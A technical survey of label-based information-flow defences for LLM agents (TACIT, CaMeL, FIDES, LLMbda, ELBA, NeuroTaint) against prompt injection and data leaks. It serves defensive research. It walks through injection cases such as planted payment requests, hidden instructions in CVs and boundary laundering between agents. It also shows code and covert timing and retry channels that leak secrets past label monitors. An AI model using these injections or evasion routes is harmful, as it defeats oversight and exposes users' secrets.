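TACIT and CaMeL each stopped all but one of more than 1,800 attacks. TACIT's exception was in a travel task with o4-mini. The user asked the agent to book one hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a second hotel in the first one's reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews in its answer. AgentDojo counted the attack as successful because the answer contained the second hotel's name.

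No secret leaked, and the policy allowed public reviews to reach the user, so this was not a failure of the type system.

LACUNA completed more tasks than TACIT in seven of the eight comparisons. Seven of the eight attacks that succeeded against it were in runs with Gemini.

### When the next step depends on a secret

One AgentDojo task asks the agent to find a new colleague's address on her website and invite her to Slack. In TACIT's version, the web page arrives as a `Classified[String]`, but the invitation tool needs an ordinary `String`. If `map` accepts only functions without side effects, no program can get the address from the page to the tool. The same problem arises when an agent has to pay a bill whose amount is in a classified file.

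Local purity also rules out data-dependent actions, such as creating a calendar event only if a private email asks for one, unless the user reads the answer and takes the last step.

The AgentDojo version of TACIT probably allowed some of these tasks, because its compiler apparently would have let an agent call the tools for sending money and messages inside `map`. If agents did this, TACIT's scores include tasks that strict local purity would forbid, and a stricter version would complete fewer tasks.

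It would also mean that the attack results provide little evidence about local purity. An injection in a boxed email fails mainly because the model writing the program never reads it, as in Willison's dual-LLM pattern. The injection could still corrupt a value that the second model returns, such as the account number for a payment.

The leak test doesn't measure this loss of completed work either. Its published examples of legitimate work with secrets are a summary and a set of anonymised reviews, and both can stay in a box until the user reads them.

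### Ordinary work in Scala

To find out whether writing Scala makes agents worse at their jobs, Odersky and colleagues used the airline and retail settings of τ²-bench, the customer-service benchmark. They ran each task ten times. Agents that wrote Scala did slightly better than agents that called tools directly:

| Model | Airline, direct calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, direct calls | Retail, TACIT |
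|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

The gains range from 0.8 to 3.7 points. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it, a difference of five problems. Odersky and colleagues suggest that programming relies more on shell commands, which are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

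The paper attributes the τ²-bench gains to the typed interface. The Scala agents receive an order, for example, as an object with named fields, whereas the ordinary agent gets raw JSON text. If a Scala agent passes the wrong kind of value, the compiler reports the error before the program runs. But the Scala agents could also combine several calls, loops and calculations in one program. The experiment didn't include agents writing untyped code, such as Python, so it can't separate the benefit of types from the benefit of writing programs.

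Compilation errors were a small burden. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of the snippets needed a retry, depending on the model and setting, and those needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. A typical mistake was writing `$50` in text, where Scala treats the dollar sign as the start of a variable name. Compiling usually took less than a second, so most of the delay came from asking the model again.

LACUNA did much worse on the same benchmark. In retail, it solved 58.8% of tasks with DeepSeek V4 Flash, while the ordinary agent solved 80.9%. The compiler rejected 22.4% of its retail snippets. With Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the rejection rate was 3.2% in retail and 89% in telecom. Zhao and colleagues suspect that models were trained on too little Scala. Writing code for LACUNA is also harder, because the code has to fit into a program that is already running. In addition, the researchers had turned off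 the models' reasoning. TACIT's low retry rate may therefore not carry over to other typed agents.

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) report "no significant loss in task performance" in *Securing Agents With Tracked Capabilities*, the conference version of the TACIT paper. The τ²-bench and SWE-bench results support this for agents that can see their data. The airline and retail tools return customer records as ordinary values, with no `Classified` boxes, so those tests measure how writing Scala affects performance, but not how hiding information that the agent needs would affect it.

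### Newer models, with policies on and off

No outside group seems to have repeated TACIT's leak test. The closest independent evidence comes from *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026). Its system, ELBA, has a model write typed Haskell programs and uses the LIO library to check labels while they run. The researchers could turn off the data-flow policies and keep the typed code, which separates the policies' effect on completed work from that of the typed code.

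They tested ELBA and CaMeL on AgentDojo's Slack setting with newer models. Without attacks, the systems completed this many of the 21 tasks:

| Model | ELBA, no policies | ELBA, policies | CaMeL, no policies | CaMeL, policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 18 | 10 | 15 | 5 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 16 | 9 | 16 | 6 |
| GPT-5.4 | 16 | 10 | 17 | 5 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 14 | 8 | 13 | 4 |

Models could complete most of the tasks in typed Haskell, and many of the failures without policies were refusals by the model. With the policies on, ELBA lost about four tasks in ten and CaMeL about two in three. This suggests that restrictions on data reduce completed work much more than the typed language does. ELBA's lead over CaMeL is uncertain because there were only 21 tasks, but it also held for every model in the larger set of runs under attack.

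The results also complicate TACIT's comparison with CaMeL. In Slack runs under attack, CaMeL completed 21% to 29% of tasks with policies and 52% to 80% without them. Odersky and colleagues don't say whether the CaMeL figures they borrowed came from runs with policies. CaMeL's 68.6% in the TACIT comparison falls in the second range, which suggests runs without policies, but the models and set-ups differ too much to be sure. If the runs had no policies, part of CaMeL's lead came from weaker protection.

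Both systems resisted all of the benchmark's Slack attacks with every model, even without policies, so these attacks are now too weak to show what a defence adds. Zhou and colleagues therefore made the injections succeed: whenever a sub-agent received text containing an attack, they replaced its whole prompt with that text, so that it followed the attacker's orders.

Each model went through 735 of these trials. Without policies, between 16% and 42% of the attacks succeeded, depending on the model, and with policies none did. The policies also cut the share of legitimate tasks completed from 67–76% to 40–48%. A similar test of TACIT would be more informative than another round of standard injections, because the result would depend much less on whether the model spots the attack.

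ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL, mainly because it prompts the model for more code after receiving new data. Retries after compilation errors took only 3.4% of the time.

Typed code can also reduce computation. In a separate test, agents searched the web and compiled bibliographies. ELBA's types allowed only entries fetched from a trusted database. ELBA produced no false citations among 925, while an ordinary agent produced 19 among 1,002. The ordinary agent used about four times as many model calls and 65 times as many input tokens.

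### The cost of building an interface

A firm also has to describe its tools in Scala. TACIT has about 1,000 lines of shared code, and the airline and retail interfaces add a few hundred lines each. Each interface is about as long as the JSON descriptions it replaces. Odersky and colleagues suggest that agents could draft new interfaces for people to review.

The line counts are a poor measure of the skill required. To add a database, for example, lampepfl tells developers to define a new permission and the form of the results, write the operations, connect them to the library and rebuild it. In the version that used a pattern search, they also had to list forbidden code to stop an agent from contacting the database directly. If a developer forgets to mark the new permission as a capability, the compiler can't track it, and agent code could keep it after its block ends. The project also depended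 on nightly builds of an experimental compiler, whose behaviour could change between versions.

Agents also need instructions. The shared prompt for AgentDojo is about 170 lines long and covers how the boxes work and which way of writing a function will compile. An agent normally sends such a prompt to the model at every step, so the firm keeps paying for it. The firm also needs a trusted model that is good enough to read the secrets. If it runs this model on its own machines, the hardware could easily cost more than the Scala code.

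## Which leaks can get past label tracking?

Label tracking can miss implicit flows, in which an outsider works out a secret from the agent's choice of actions, because the secret text itself never moves. TACIT's leak test searched the agent's output for secret text, and AgentDojo checks whether an attacker achieved a goal, so neither would detect such a leak.

### The branch that didn't run

Suppose an agent's program contains these lines, where `clause_changed` comes from a secret contract:

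```
changed = False
if clause_changed:
    changed = True
if not changed:
    send_email(supplier, "Nothing to discuss this week.")
```

The email contains no contract text. To catch the flow, a run-time monitor has to label the program counter, which records the program's current position, as well as the data. Fenton proposed this in the 1970s for an abstract computer, the Data Mark Machine, which Denning describes. When the program enters a branch that depends on a secret, the machine raises the program counter's label. Everything the program writes inside the branch must be at least that restricted. At the end of the branch, the machine restores the old label.

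A monitor that lets labels change during a run would therefore mark `changed` as secret when the third line runs. If the clause hasn't changed, the third line doesn't run, `changed` stays public, and the monitor allows the email. If the clause has changed, the program doesn't try to send the email, so the monitor has nothing to block. The supplier gets the message only when the clause is unchanged.

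In this program, `changed` is secret in one run and public in the other, so the monitor would block an email that the program tried to send because the clause had changed. A second variable removes that obstacle:

```
unsure = True
changed = True
if clause_changed:
    unsure = False
if unsure:
    changed = False
if changed:
    send_email(supplier, "Please call us.")
```

| | Clause has changed | Clause hasn't changed |
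|---|---|---|
| `unsure` after the first `if` | False, secret | True, public |
| `changed` after the second `if` | True, public | False, public |
| Result | the email goes out | no email |

The value of `changed` now matches the secret exactly, and its label is public in both runs. The monitor never blocks anything.

### Ways to close the gap

One remedy is to fix every variable's label in advance. If `unsure` is permanently public, the machine blocks any change to it inside the secret branch, so it has the same value in both runs. Fenton proved that with fixed labels, checking only the writes that actually happen is enough. Fixed labels are awkward for agents, which often learn a document's label only when they fetch it.

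Another approach is to examine both branches before the program runs. Denning's rule is that if a condition has label C, and its branches could write to variables with labels B₁ to Bₙ, then C ⊑ Bᵢ must hold for every i. *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977) showed how a compiler could check this. CaMeL's main model writes its whole program in advance, so a similar check seems feasible, although some labels would still be unknown.

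A monitor can also follow a rule called no high upgrade, which stops the program whenever code in a secret branch tries to change a public variable. If the clause has changed, the monitor would stop the second program at `unsure = False`. Otherwise, the program would finish without sending anything, so the supplier would get no email either way. Anyone who can tell whether the program finished would still learn whether the clause has changed. The rule also stops some harmless programs.

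### What FIDES guarantees instead

Costa and colleagues prove that their labelled agent loop can enforce a weaker property than noninterference, called explicit secrecy. Let d₁ and d₂ be two states of the stored data that differ only in their secrets, written d₁ =<sub>L</sub> d₂. Suppose the agent starts from d₁ and makes some tool calls. Let g be the function that applies those same calls to any starting state. Explicit secrecy requires that

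g(d₁) =<sub>L</sub> g(d₂).

In other words, replaying the calls with different secrets must give the same public data. Noninterference instead compares what outsiders observe in the two runs when the agent starts afresh from d₂ and chooses its own calls.

| What the agent does | Explicit secrecy | Noninterference |
|---|---|---|
| Copies a contract into a public file | violated | violated |
| Sets off a public alert only if a clause has changed | satisfied | violated |
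| Sets off the same alert every time | satisfied | satisfied |

Costa and colleagues chose the weaker property because noninterference would forbid almost any public action after the agent had read a secret. They note the same compromise in web browsers and in TaintDroid, a tracking system for phones.

Their reason is convincing for an agent that reads secrets into its context, since anything there may affect its next choice. It is less convincing for agents that keep secrets in variables or boxes, because the planner can't base a choice on text it hasn't read. How much noninterference restricts these agents depends on how many tasks require the planner to read the secrets.

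The gap in FIDES is also narrower than the definition suggests. Once the planner has read a contract, the words it writes carry the contract's label, so an email containing those words can fail the permitted-flow check even if they reveal nothing. The clearest remaining leak is a call with no arguments, because making the call can itself convey information. If an outsider could observe two such calls, a hostile instruction might have the agent spell out a password in binary, using one call for 0 and the other for 1.

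The proof also assumes a model that always gives the same answer to the same input, and it leaves out timing and the length of network packets.

### The gaps in CaMeL

CaMeL does track branches to some extent. For example, it can refuse a call that sends an email inside a branch that depends on an account balance. But *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), which introduces the LLMbda calculus, found that CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that runs. The paper demonstrates the leak with a program like the second one above, based on an example by Fenton.

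CaMeL has a second leak outside its interpreter. When a program fails, CaMeL can have its main model write a new one and try again, using an ordinary Python loop that carries no labels. Whether the policy blocked an attempt may depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. Most information-flow systems tolerate one such bit per run, but CaMeL's loop allows each attempt to test something new about the secret. A 16-digit account number could therefore be recovered in about 54 attempts. CaMeL censors its error messages to reduce this risk, but there is no proof that this is enough.

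Garby and colleagues also note that inserting an untrusted value into a text template makes CaMeL treat the value as trusted.

How much these gaps matter depends on who writes the program. CaMeL's main model writes its first program before any tool has returned data, so an outside attacker can't simply add leaking code. A firm that trusts the main model mostly has to worry about accidental leaks, which are plausible because setting a flag to `False` and changing it inside a branch is an ordinary way to program. A malicious model could use all three gaps on purpose.

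### Conversations with labels

The LLMbda calculus is a small programming language for agents. Its designers wanted one proof to cover every agent anyone could write in it, including agents that generate and run code. FIDES's guarantee applies to one form of agent loop, and CaMeL has no comparable theorem.

Every value in the calculus has a label, and so does the conversation with the model. The conversation's label is the join of the labels of everything the program has sent to the model. The model's reply takes this label, and if the reply is code, the code runs under it. Code generated after the model receives a hostile email therefore can't escape the restrictions on that email.

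A program can copy the conversation with `fork` and empty it with `clear`. An agent could therefore summarise a contract like this:

```
fork (let _ = clear in @("Summarise: " + contract))
```

The line runs in four steps:

1. `fork` saves the current conversation.
2. `clear` removes all earlier messages from the working copy.
3. `@` sends the request and the contract to the model and gets the summary.
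4. `fork` discards the working copy and restores the saved conversation.

The summary keeps the contract's label, and the main conversation never contains the contract or the summary. This one line of code serves the same purpose as Willison's quarantined model, so the programmer can decide where to isolate text instead of building the whole agent around two models.

The calculus applies the no-high-upgrade rule to conversations. A program stops if it tries to send a message to a public conversation from inside a secret branch.

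### A guarantee for a random program

A language model's outputs are random, so the same program can produce different results from identical data. Noninterference must therefore compare the probabilities of results. It must also account for runs that never finish or that stop at a failed check.

Garby and colleagues call their version termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference. Let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities that an observer gets result q under two different secrets. Each set of probabilities may add up to less than one, and the remainder is the chance of getting no result. The guarantee requires a third set of probabilities, ω, such that

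μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, and Σ ω(q) ≤ 1.

This means that the two sets could become identical if some of the unfinished runs had finished. Suppose that when a clause has changed, the program sends an email 60% of the time and otherwise stops before finishing. When the clause hasn't changed, it sends the email 30% of the time, finishes without sending it 40% of the time, and otherwise stops before finishing. The guarantee allows this because the larger probabilities for the two results, 60% for sending the email and 40% for finishing without sending it, add up to 100%. If the program with the unchanged clause instead sent the email 20% of the time and finished without sending it 80% of the time, the total would be 140%, and the guarantee would forbid it.

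Stopping early can still leak information, but the definition limits how much. The statistical distance between the two sets of results is at most the average of the two programs' chances of stopping early. In the permitted example, the distance and the average are both 35%. If neither program ever stops early, the two sets must be identical. The researchers first tried ignoring unfinished runs and comparing the rest, but that definition turned out to be wrong.

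Their proof uses a second way of running programs, which skips any computation whose label is too high for the observer. It gives the same probabilities whatever the secrets are and finishes at least as often as the real program, so it provides the ω that the definition requires.

### What the Lean proof covers

The researchers proved all this in Lean. The interpreter that runs the agents is also a Lean function, and they proved that its results have the probabilities the calculus predicts. They believe the interpreter is the first software for running language-model agents to have machine-checked security theorems about its own code.

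The interpreter treats the model as an unknown function that returns a reply to each conversation. When an agent runs, that function makes a network request to a real model. The guarantee depends on the connection to the model, on correct labels and on correct checks in the tools. The theorems also assume that every data source is part of the program, which isn't true of a real mail server or bank. The researchers list this as a limitation.

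### The banking test

To test the calculus, Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called RANDORI. The model writes a program for the user's task and tries it on an artificial bank account. If the program fails, the model can repair it and try again. The agent runs the program on the benchmark account only after this practice. Errors during practice contain no information about that account, so RANDORI avoids the leak in CaMeL's retry loop.

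They ran RANDORI and CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each. Without attacks, they completed these shares of the tasks:

| System | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| RANDORI, with label checks | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| CaMeL, without policies | 66.7% | 70.8% |
| CaMeL, with policies | 37.5% | 37.5% |

RANDORI's scores are similar to those of CaMeL without policies, but there were so few tasks that the margins of error are around 20 points. Under attack, CaMeL without policies scored higher than RANDORI, by 6 points with GPT-5.2 and 13 points with MiMo. Those two differences are based on only about a third of the planned CaMeL runs.

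The comparison with CaMeL's policies switched on isn't entirely fair, because RANDORI implements only some of them and lets its programs declare particular pieces of untrusted data to be trusted. Without that permission, RANDORI's score with MiMo fell to 54.2%, still well above CaMeL's 37.5%.

RANDORI resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks across three models. In about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attack required a tool call that would never appear in a program for the user's task. Separating planning from reading defeats these attacks without any labels. Both failures were among the 423 runs of the remaining, harder combinations.

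Both came from GPT-5.2 on the same task, under the same attack. The user asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a fraudulent payment request. The agent's program declared the file's contents trusted, so the payment passed the check. Labels record where text came from, and the genuine and fraudulent bills came from the same place. A strict policy would block the fraud but also stop the agent from completing the task.

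None of these attacks tries to infer a secret from the agent's pattern of actions, so for implicit flows the evidence is the proof.

### Time and termination

A noninterference proof rules out only leaks that an observer, as the proof defines it, could detect. The LLMbda semantics has no clock, so its proof does not cover timing leaks. Odersky and colleagues also exclude timing and termination from TACIT's guarantee. In their example, an agent leaks one bit by making a function inside `map` take longer for some contents than for others.

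A pure function can still leak information through its running time. It might do a long calculation if the contract has a penalty clause and return at once if it doesn't. The result stays hidden from the cloud model, but the model can observe the delay, which reveals whether the clause is there. A function that never finishes in one of the two cases would leak the same information.

A one-bit leak can add up because the agent can submit more programs. At one bit per request, a malicious model could read a 128-bit key in 128 requests, but would need many thousands to read a long contract. Short secrets such as passwords are therefore at greater risk from slow leaks than long documents are.

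TACIT could hide the difference by sending every reply after the same delay and putting a failure value in the box if the function hadn't finished. With a ten-second delay, even the quickest request would take ten seconds.

### Lampson's confinement problem

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, described this kind of difficulty for shared computers. A customer gives confidential data to a service, which is a program written by somebody else. The confinement problem is to stop the service from passing the data to its owner. Several of Lampson's examples have close counterparts in agents:

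| Leak in Lampson's paper | Counterpart in an agent |
|---|---|
| The service remembers data until its owner calls it | The trusted model uses a contract when answering a later request |
| The service encodes data in its bill | The number of paid calls to an outside service depends on a secret |
| The service opens and closes a file, and its owner tests whether the file is in use | The agent reads secrets from the sizes of classified files |
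| The service changes the load on the computer | The agent measures how long TACIT takes to reply |

Lampson divided the routes into three kinds. Storage channels are places that one program can write to and another can read. Legitimate channels, such as the bill, carry information that the owner is supposed to get. Covert channels, such as the computer's load, are not meant to carry information. Denning's lattice model covers the first two kinds but leaves out covert channels.

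Total isolation would solve the problem, but Lampson considered it impractical. His alternative was to let the customer decide what enters each channel. For instance, the customer could calculate the bill, and the service could accept or reject it. To hide the program's effect on system load, the operating system might have to slow the program down or make unnecessary disk accesses. Lampson doubted that anyone could rigorously identify every channel in even a moderately complex system.

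According to lecture notes from Purdue University, Lipner concluded in 1975 that systems could close storage and legitimate channels with little overhead, but that closing covert channels would slow them down unreasonably. Lampson's less demanding option was to limit how much information a covert channel can carry. However, a single bit can reveal whether a firm is about to drop a supplier, and Schroeder de Witt (2026), in *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem*, points out that a small leak can still do great harm if a capable agent chooses what to send.

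### When hostile data chooses the branch

Branches also create a problem for integrity. In branch steering, an attacker's data, rather than a secret, determines which branch runs. The attacker can't add steps to the program but can choose which of its existing steps run.

Choosing which branch runs gives an attacker little power if every branch is harmless, but a program can contain too many branches. One AgentDojo banking task tells the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. In tests by Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's main model sometimes wrote a loop that read each instruction and had a branch for every tool. With the policies off, an attacker who controlled the file could use any of those tools. Two attacks succeeded this way, although the attacker's text never reached the main model.

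Labels can prevent branch steering if the program counter carries integrity labels too. A payment inside a branch that depends on untrusted data is then an untrusted action, and a policy can block it. FIDES offers similar protection because its planner must read the untrusted answer before acting on it, which normally makes the context untrusted.

### Agents that use a screen

This defence relies on knowing which actions are dangerous. That is difficult for computer-use agents, which work by viewing a screen, clicking and typing. A click might close a window, delete a file or open a malicious site, so a policy on the click tool can't block only the dangerous clicks.

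Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) adapted CaMeL to such agents. The planner writes a complete program without seeing the screen. A separate model looks at the screen, answers questions such as whether a cookie notice is visible, and finds where to click. The programs must anticipate many possible screens, so they average about 40 branches, compared with fewer than 4 in CaMeL's AgentDojo programs.

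The researchers, who ran this system without data-flow policies, then put a fake cookie notice in an advertisement. The program already contained a step for dismissing cookie notices. The screen-reading model directed the click to the advertisement, which led to the attacker's site even though the agent had followed its plan exactly.

The researchers tried two defences. One compared the screen with the page's underlying code. It stopped the attack on simple banners, where the code still identified the advertisement, but failed when the attacker could replace that code. The other used a second model to check the first model's answer. Small changes to an advertisement's pixels defeated this check, even when it was set so strictly that it often rejected legitimate actions.

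The design also completed far fewer tasks. Foerster and colleagues say it retained up to 57% of the performance of frontier models. For that figure, a task counted as solved if any of five attempts succeeded. The 109 tasks used seem to be those the unprotected Claude agent had completed. With one attempt per task, the protected agent completed 28%.

### Agents that call other agents

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* examines a different gap, which appears when one CaMeL agent gives work to another. In its example, a user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to a colleague on Slack. A database agent fetches the records, a coordinating agent has them summarised, and a notification agent sends the message. An attacker has hidden an instruction in the database.

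The first two agents keep the instruction away from their main models. But the coordinator inserts the summary into its request to the notification agent. That agent treats the whole request as coming from its user, so its main model reads the hidden instruction and adds an email to the attacker. Each agent's tracking works correctly, but the text loses its untrusted status when it passes between agents, which the paper calls boundary laundering.

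Its solution, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data separately. The interpreter rejects a request if its instructions depend on anything a tool returned. The receiving agent gets tool output in variables that its main model can't read, with the labels still attached.

The test used a version of AgentDojo that divides the tools among several agents. Averaged over five models, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL on its own, and none with multi-CaMeL. Every attack that got past the separate CaMeL agents used boundary laundering. The rate is low partly because the benchmark's attacks are weak: none of them succeeded against GPT-5.5, even with no defence.

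Multi-CaMeL still permits branch steering. A tool's result can determine which of two requests the coordinator sends, if both are in its program. Multi-CaMeL also inherits CaMeL's missed branches because it uses an extended version of the same interpreter. It doesn't retry failed programs, so it avoids the leak in CaMeL's retry loop.

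## Why do labels spread until an agent can do little, and can that be limited?

In ordinary code, each line shows which values go into a result. After `c = a + b`, the label of `c` is just the join of the labels of `a` and `b`. A language model instead writes text one token (a word or part of a word) at a time, and computes each token from all the tokens before it, including those it has just written. Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026) point out in *GIF* that any input token may therefore influence any output token.

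The safe rule, which FIDES follows, is to give every output the join of the labels of everything in the context. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* accepts that nothing better is available for now, but warns that under this rule every piece of data ends up labelled as "everything", the extreme form of label creep, and the labels no longer serve a purpose.

### One email and a blocked notice

Suppose Ann gives an agent two jobs in one conversation. First, it has to look up the time of a disciplinary hearing in an email from Hana in personnel and add it to Ann's private calendar. Then it has to announce on the firm's public website that the office is closed on Friday.

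| Step | Who may read the context | Check |
|---|---|---|
| Ann makes both requests | everyone | none needed |
| The agent reads Hana's email | Ann and Hana | none needed |
| The agent adds the hearing to Ann's calendar | Ann and Hana | passes |
| The agent tries to publish the notice about Friday | Ann and Hana | fails |

Everything in the notice came from Ann's own request. The checker can't verify this, because the model also had the email in its context when it wrote the notice and could have included something from it.

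The agent could have avoided the problem by publishing the notice first or by starting a new conversation for it. However, somebody has to know in advance which jobs are independent, and an agent often finds out what it needs to read only as it works.

Reader lists can shrink quickly. Suppose each document an agent reads has an independent 10% chance of being closed to a particular colleague. After 20 documents, the chance that this colleague is still allowed to see the agent's output is 0.9²⁰, or about 12%. In a real firm the decline would probably be slower, because the same teams tend to have access to the same documents.

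### Dividing the work among several agents

The firm could give Ann's two jobs to separate agents, each with its own context. In *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) simulated how much such arrangements can help, without running a language model. A typical task had 20 tool calls, divided among five agents, and some calls needed the results of others. Some calls introduced a sensitive label. Any agent that received this label kept it for the rest of the task and attached it to everything it passed on.

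The researchers measured "utility loss" as the share of tool calls that introduced a sensitive label or ran in an agent that already had one. This is a proxy for lost work, since the simulation had no real tasks.

The shape of the network affects how labels spread, because two agents without a direct link have to communicate through others, which pick up the labels on the way. In a star-shaped network, the central coordinator soon has every label. When 4 of the 20 calls were sensitive, the star lost about 5 percentage points more than an ideal network with only the direct links the task needed. A hierarchy lost about 4 points more than the ideal network, and a ring about 3. A full mesh, in which every agent can contact every other, did as well as the ideal network.

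Across nine simulated networks, those with a larger share of their possible links lost less utility, with a rank correlation as strong as −0.96. Networks with longer average routes lost more, with a rank correlation of 0.87 when half the calls were sensitive. Nine networks is a small sample, and the simulation's rules partly guarantee the pattern. If labels spread only through messages, they will spread less in networks with fewer intermediaries. The results illustrate the mechanism but can't be used to estimate how many tasks a firm's own agents would lose.

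Using more agents also reduced the loss, but each link between agents is another channel to monitor, and a full mesh has 10 links with 5 agents and 190 with 20. It was less work to give the sensitive tools to a few agents instead of spreading them around, and this reduced the loss in every network. Ann's firm could have one agent that reads personnel mail and another that publishes notices.

No arrangement removed the loss entirely, because a call that depends on a sensitive result must run with a sensitive label even in the ideal network. Gregory and colleagues conclude that agents also need some form of declassification, which is the deliberate, authorised lowering of labels.

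The way they measure loss also makes some of it unavoidable. If 10 of the 20 calls introduce sensitive labels, the loss is at least 50% regardless of the network's structure. The call that reads Hana's email counts as a loss even though it succeeds, and so does the calendar entry that only Ann can see. A policy that checks who receives the data could allow both.

### How finely to label a context

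A system can also label parts of a context separately. Traditional systems can label a single variable, a file or a whole process. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* notes that a context has no equally natural units, because the boundaries between tokens don't show which stretches of text should share a label. The paper suggests dividing the context by message, by the sender's role (system, user or tool) or, for a web agent, by the site each passage came from.

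Finer labels on the input don't help by themselves, because if the system can't determine which passages the model used, it still has to label the output with the join of all their labels. Researchers have therefore tried to work out which parts of the input a particular output depends on.

### Answering again without the secret

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2024), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, found a way to use such an estimate without having to trust it. Their system works in four steps:

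1. The model answers the question using all the documents.
2. The system looks for a less restrictive label L′ such that the same answer remains likely when the model has only the documents whose labels are at or below L′.
3. The model answers again, this time with only those documents.
4. The system returns the second answer with the label L′ and discards the first.

Step 2 scores the original answer by its negative perplexity, which is lower the more surprising the model finds the text. Let U(C) be this score with all the documents and U(C′) the score with only the permitted ones. The system accepts L′ if

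U(C) − U(C′) ≤ λ,

where λ is a tolerance chosen in advance.

In the earlier example, one contract is open to Ann, Bob and Cem, and the other to Bob, Cem and Dana. If someone asks for the notice period and both contracts give it as 90 days, either contract is enough to answer the question. The search therefore finds two acceptable labels, {Ann, Bob, Cem} and {Bob, Cem, Dana}. Neither label is less restrictive than the other, so the application can choose the first if the answer is for Ann or the second if it is for Dana. Under the ordinary join, neither Ann nor Dana could have received the answer.

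The search can make mistakes, and a hostile document can cause them. Even then, the software around the model ensures that the returned text comes from a run in which the model had only the permitted documents. If the search wrongly discards a document, the new answer may be incomplete or wrong, but it can't contain anything from that document.

The choice of label can still leak information, because the system uses the secret documents to make it. Suppose the agent publishes an answer only if the answer is labelled public. If a secret email would have changed the answer, the system labels the answer secret and the agent doesn't publish it. Someone waiting for the answer can then infer something about the email, just as an observer can infer something about a secret from a program branch that doesn't run.

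Siddiqui and colleagues tested the search on Llama-2, a family of open models from 2023. In one test, they scattered details about invented people over 128 documents, each with its own label, and gave the model 14 of these documents for each question. The search found exactly the right set of labels for 86% of the questions. Asking the model which documents it had used worked for only 2% of questions with the smaller Llama-2 model and 13% with the larger one.

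A second test used pairs of reliable and unreliable news articles. The smaller model's search improved the label in 57% of the cases where this was possible, but in 23% of the cases where it lowered the label, it discarded an article that the answer needed. When an ordinary search engine also had to find the articles, these figures became 50% and 30%. These errors reduce accuracy but don't reveal secrets, because the system writes a new answer instead of putting a new label on the original one. The rates might be worse in practice, since most of the tests gave the search the correct answer instead of the model's own.

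The search is short when there are only two labels, public and secret, but if every document has its own reader list, the number of combinations to try can grow exponentially with the number of documents.

### Removing a passage to see what changes

Other methods keep the original output and estimate which inputs shaped it. The most intuitive test is to remove an input and see whether the output changes. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Tang and colleagues, 2026) describes NeuroTaint, a system that applies a version of this test to the log of a finished run.

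It first builds a graph showing where each piece of data came from and which tools and stored notes it passed through. Then it examines each call that could do harm, such as one that sends an email. It compares the meaning of the call's arguments with the earlier data, so it can recognise a secret the agent has paraphrased. If it finds no match, it tests whether the agent would still have made the call without the suspect data. In one example, a planted search result contained an instruction to send the agent's findings to an outside address before doing anything else. The agent no longer made the call when that result was replaced with neutral text.

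Cai and colleagues built a benchmark of 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks. NeuroTaint found 93.5% of the real flows, and 92.1% of its alarms were correct. Its F1 score, which combines the two figures, was 0.928, against 0.522 for FIDES. The comparison is probably unfair to FIDES. The version they tested missed the call to the outside address. But in the design by Costa and colleagues, the context's label also covers the decision to make a call, so FIDES should have treated this call as untrusted once the agent had read the search result.

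NeuroTaint estimates flows, and it missed about one in 15. It also works after the event, so it can help a firm investigate a leak but not prevent one.

Removal tests are also weaker when the same information appears twice. If two emails contain the same password, removing either one leaves the output unchanged, so a test that removes one passage at a time detects no influence from either. Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Sightline*, measured this effect on four models. They scored a removal test by how often it ranked a passage used in the output above an unused one, where 50% is no better than guessing. Adding two more copies of the used passage to the prompt lowered the score from 93–97% to 54–69%.

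Answering again avoids this problem. The system by Siddiqui and colleagues removes every document above the permitted label at once. If a copy remains in a permitted document, the model is allowed to use it.

### Measuring the effect of a small change

GIF (Geometric Information Flow), the method by Štorek and colleagues, measures how strongly the output responds to slight changes in a passage. A model represents each token as a list of numbers called an embedding. GIF estimates how much the next token, Y, would reveal about a little random noise, U, if that noise were added to the passage's embeddings. It aims to bound the mutual information between the two, I(U; Y), which is zero if the token reveals nothing about the noise.

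Let τ be the variance of the noise, and let M be a matrix describing how strongly noise in each direction shifts the probabilities of the next token. The researchers proved in Lean that

I(U; Y) ≤ ½ log det(1 + τM) + o(τ),

where 1 is the identity matrix and o(τ) is an error that shrinks faster than τ as the noise gets smaller. The middle term is GIF's score. In practice, the software estimates a simpler quantity, the sum of M's diagonal entries, because computing M in full would be far too slow.

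In one example, an agent screening job applicants reads a CV containing a planted instruction to recommend the applicant at a salary of $200,000, and obeys it. GIF attributes 82 bits of influence on the recommendation to the planted instruction, 27 to the employer's hiring criteria and 16 to the remaining text.

The proof covers only very small changes to the embeddings, but protecting a secret requires knowing how the output would change if the text were quite different. If a model reports with near certainty that a contract has a penalty clause, slight noise won't alter the answer, so GIF's score is close to zero, even though a contract without the clause would have produced the opposite answer. Xu and colleagues proved that such scores vanish as the model's confidence approaches 100%. This matters in practice because one model they tested gave other tokens less than 1% of the probability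 in a fifth of its outputs.

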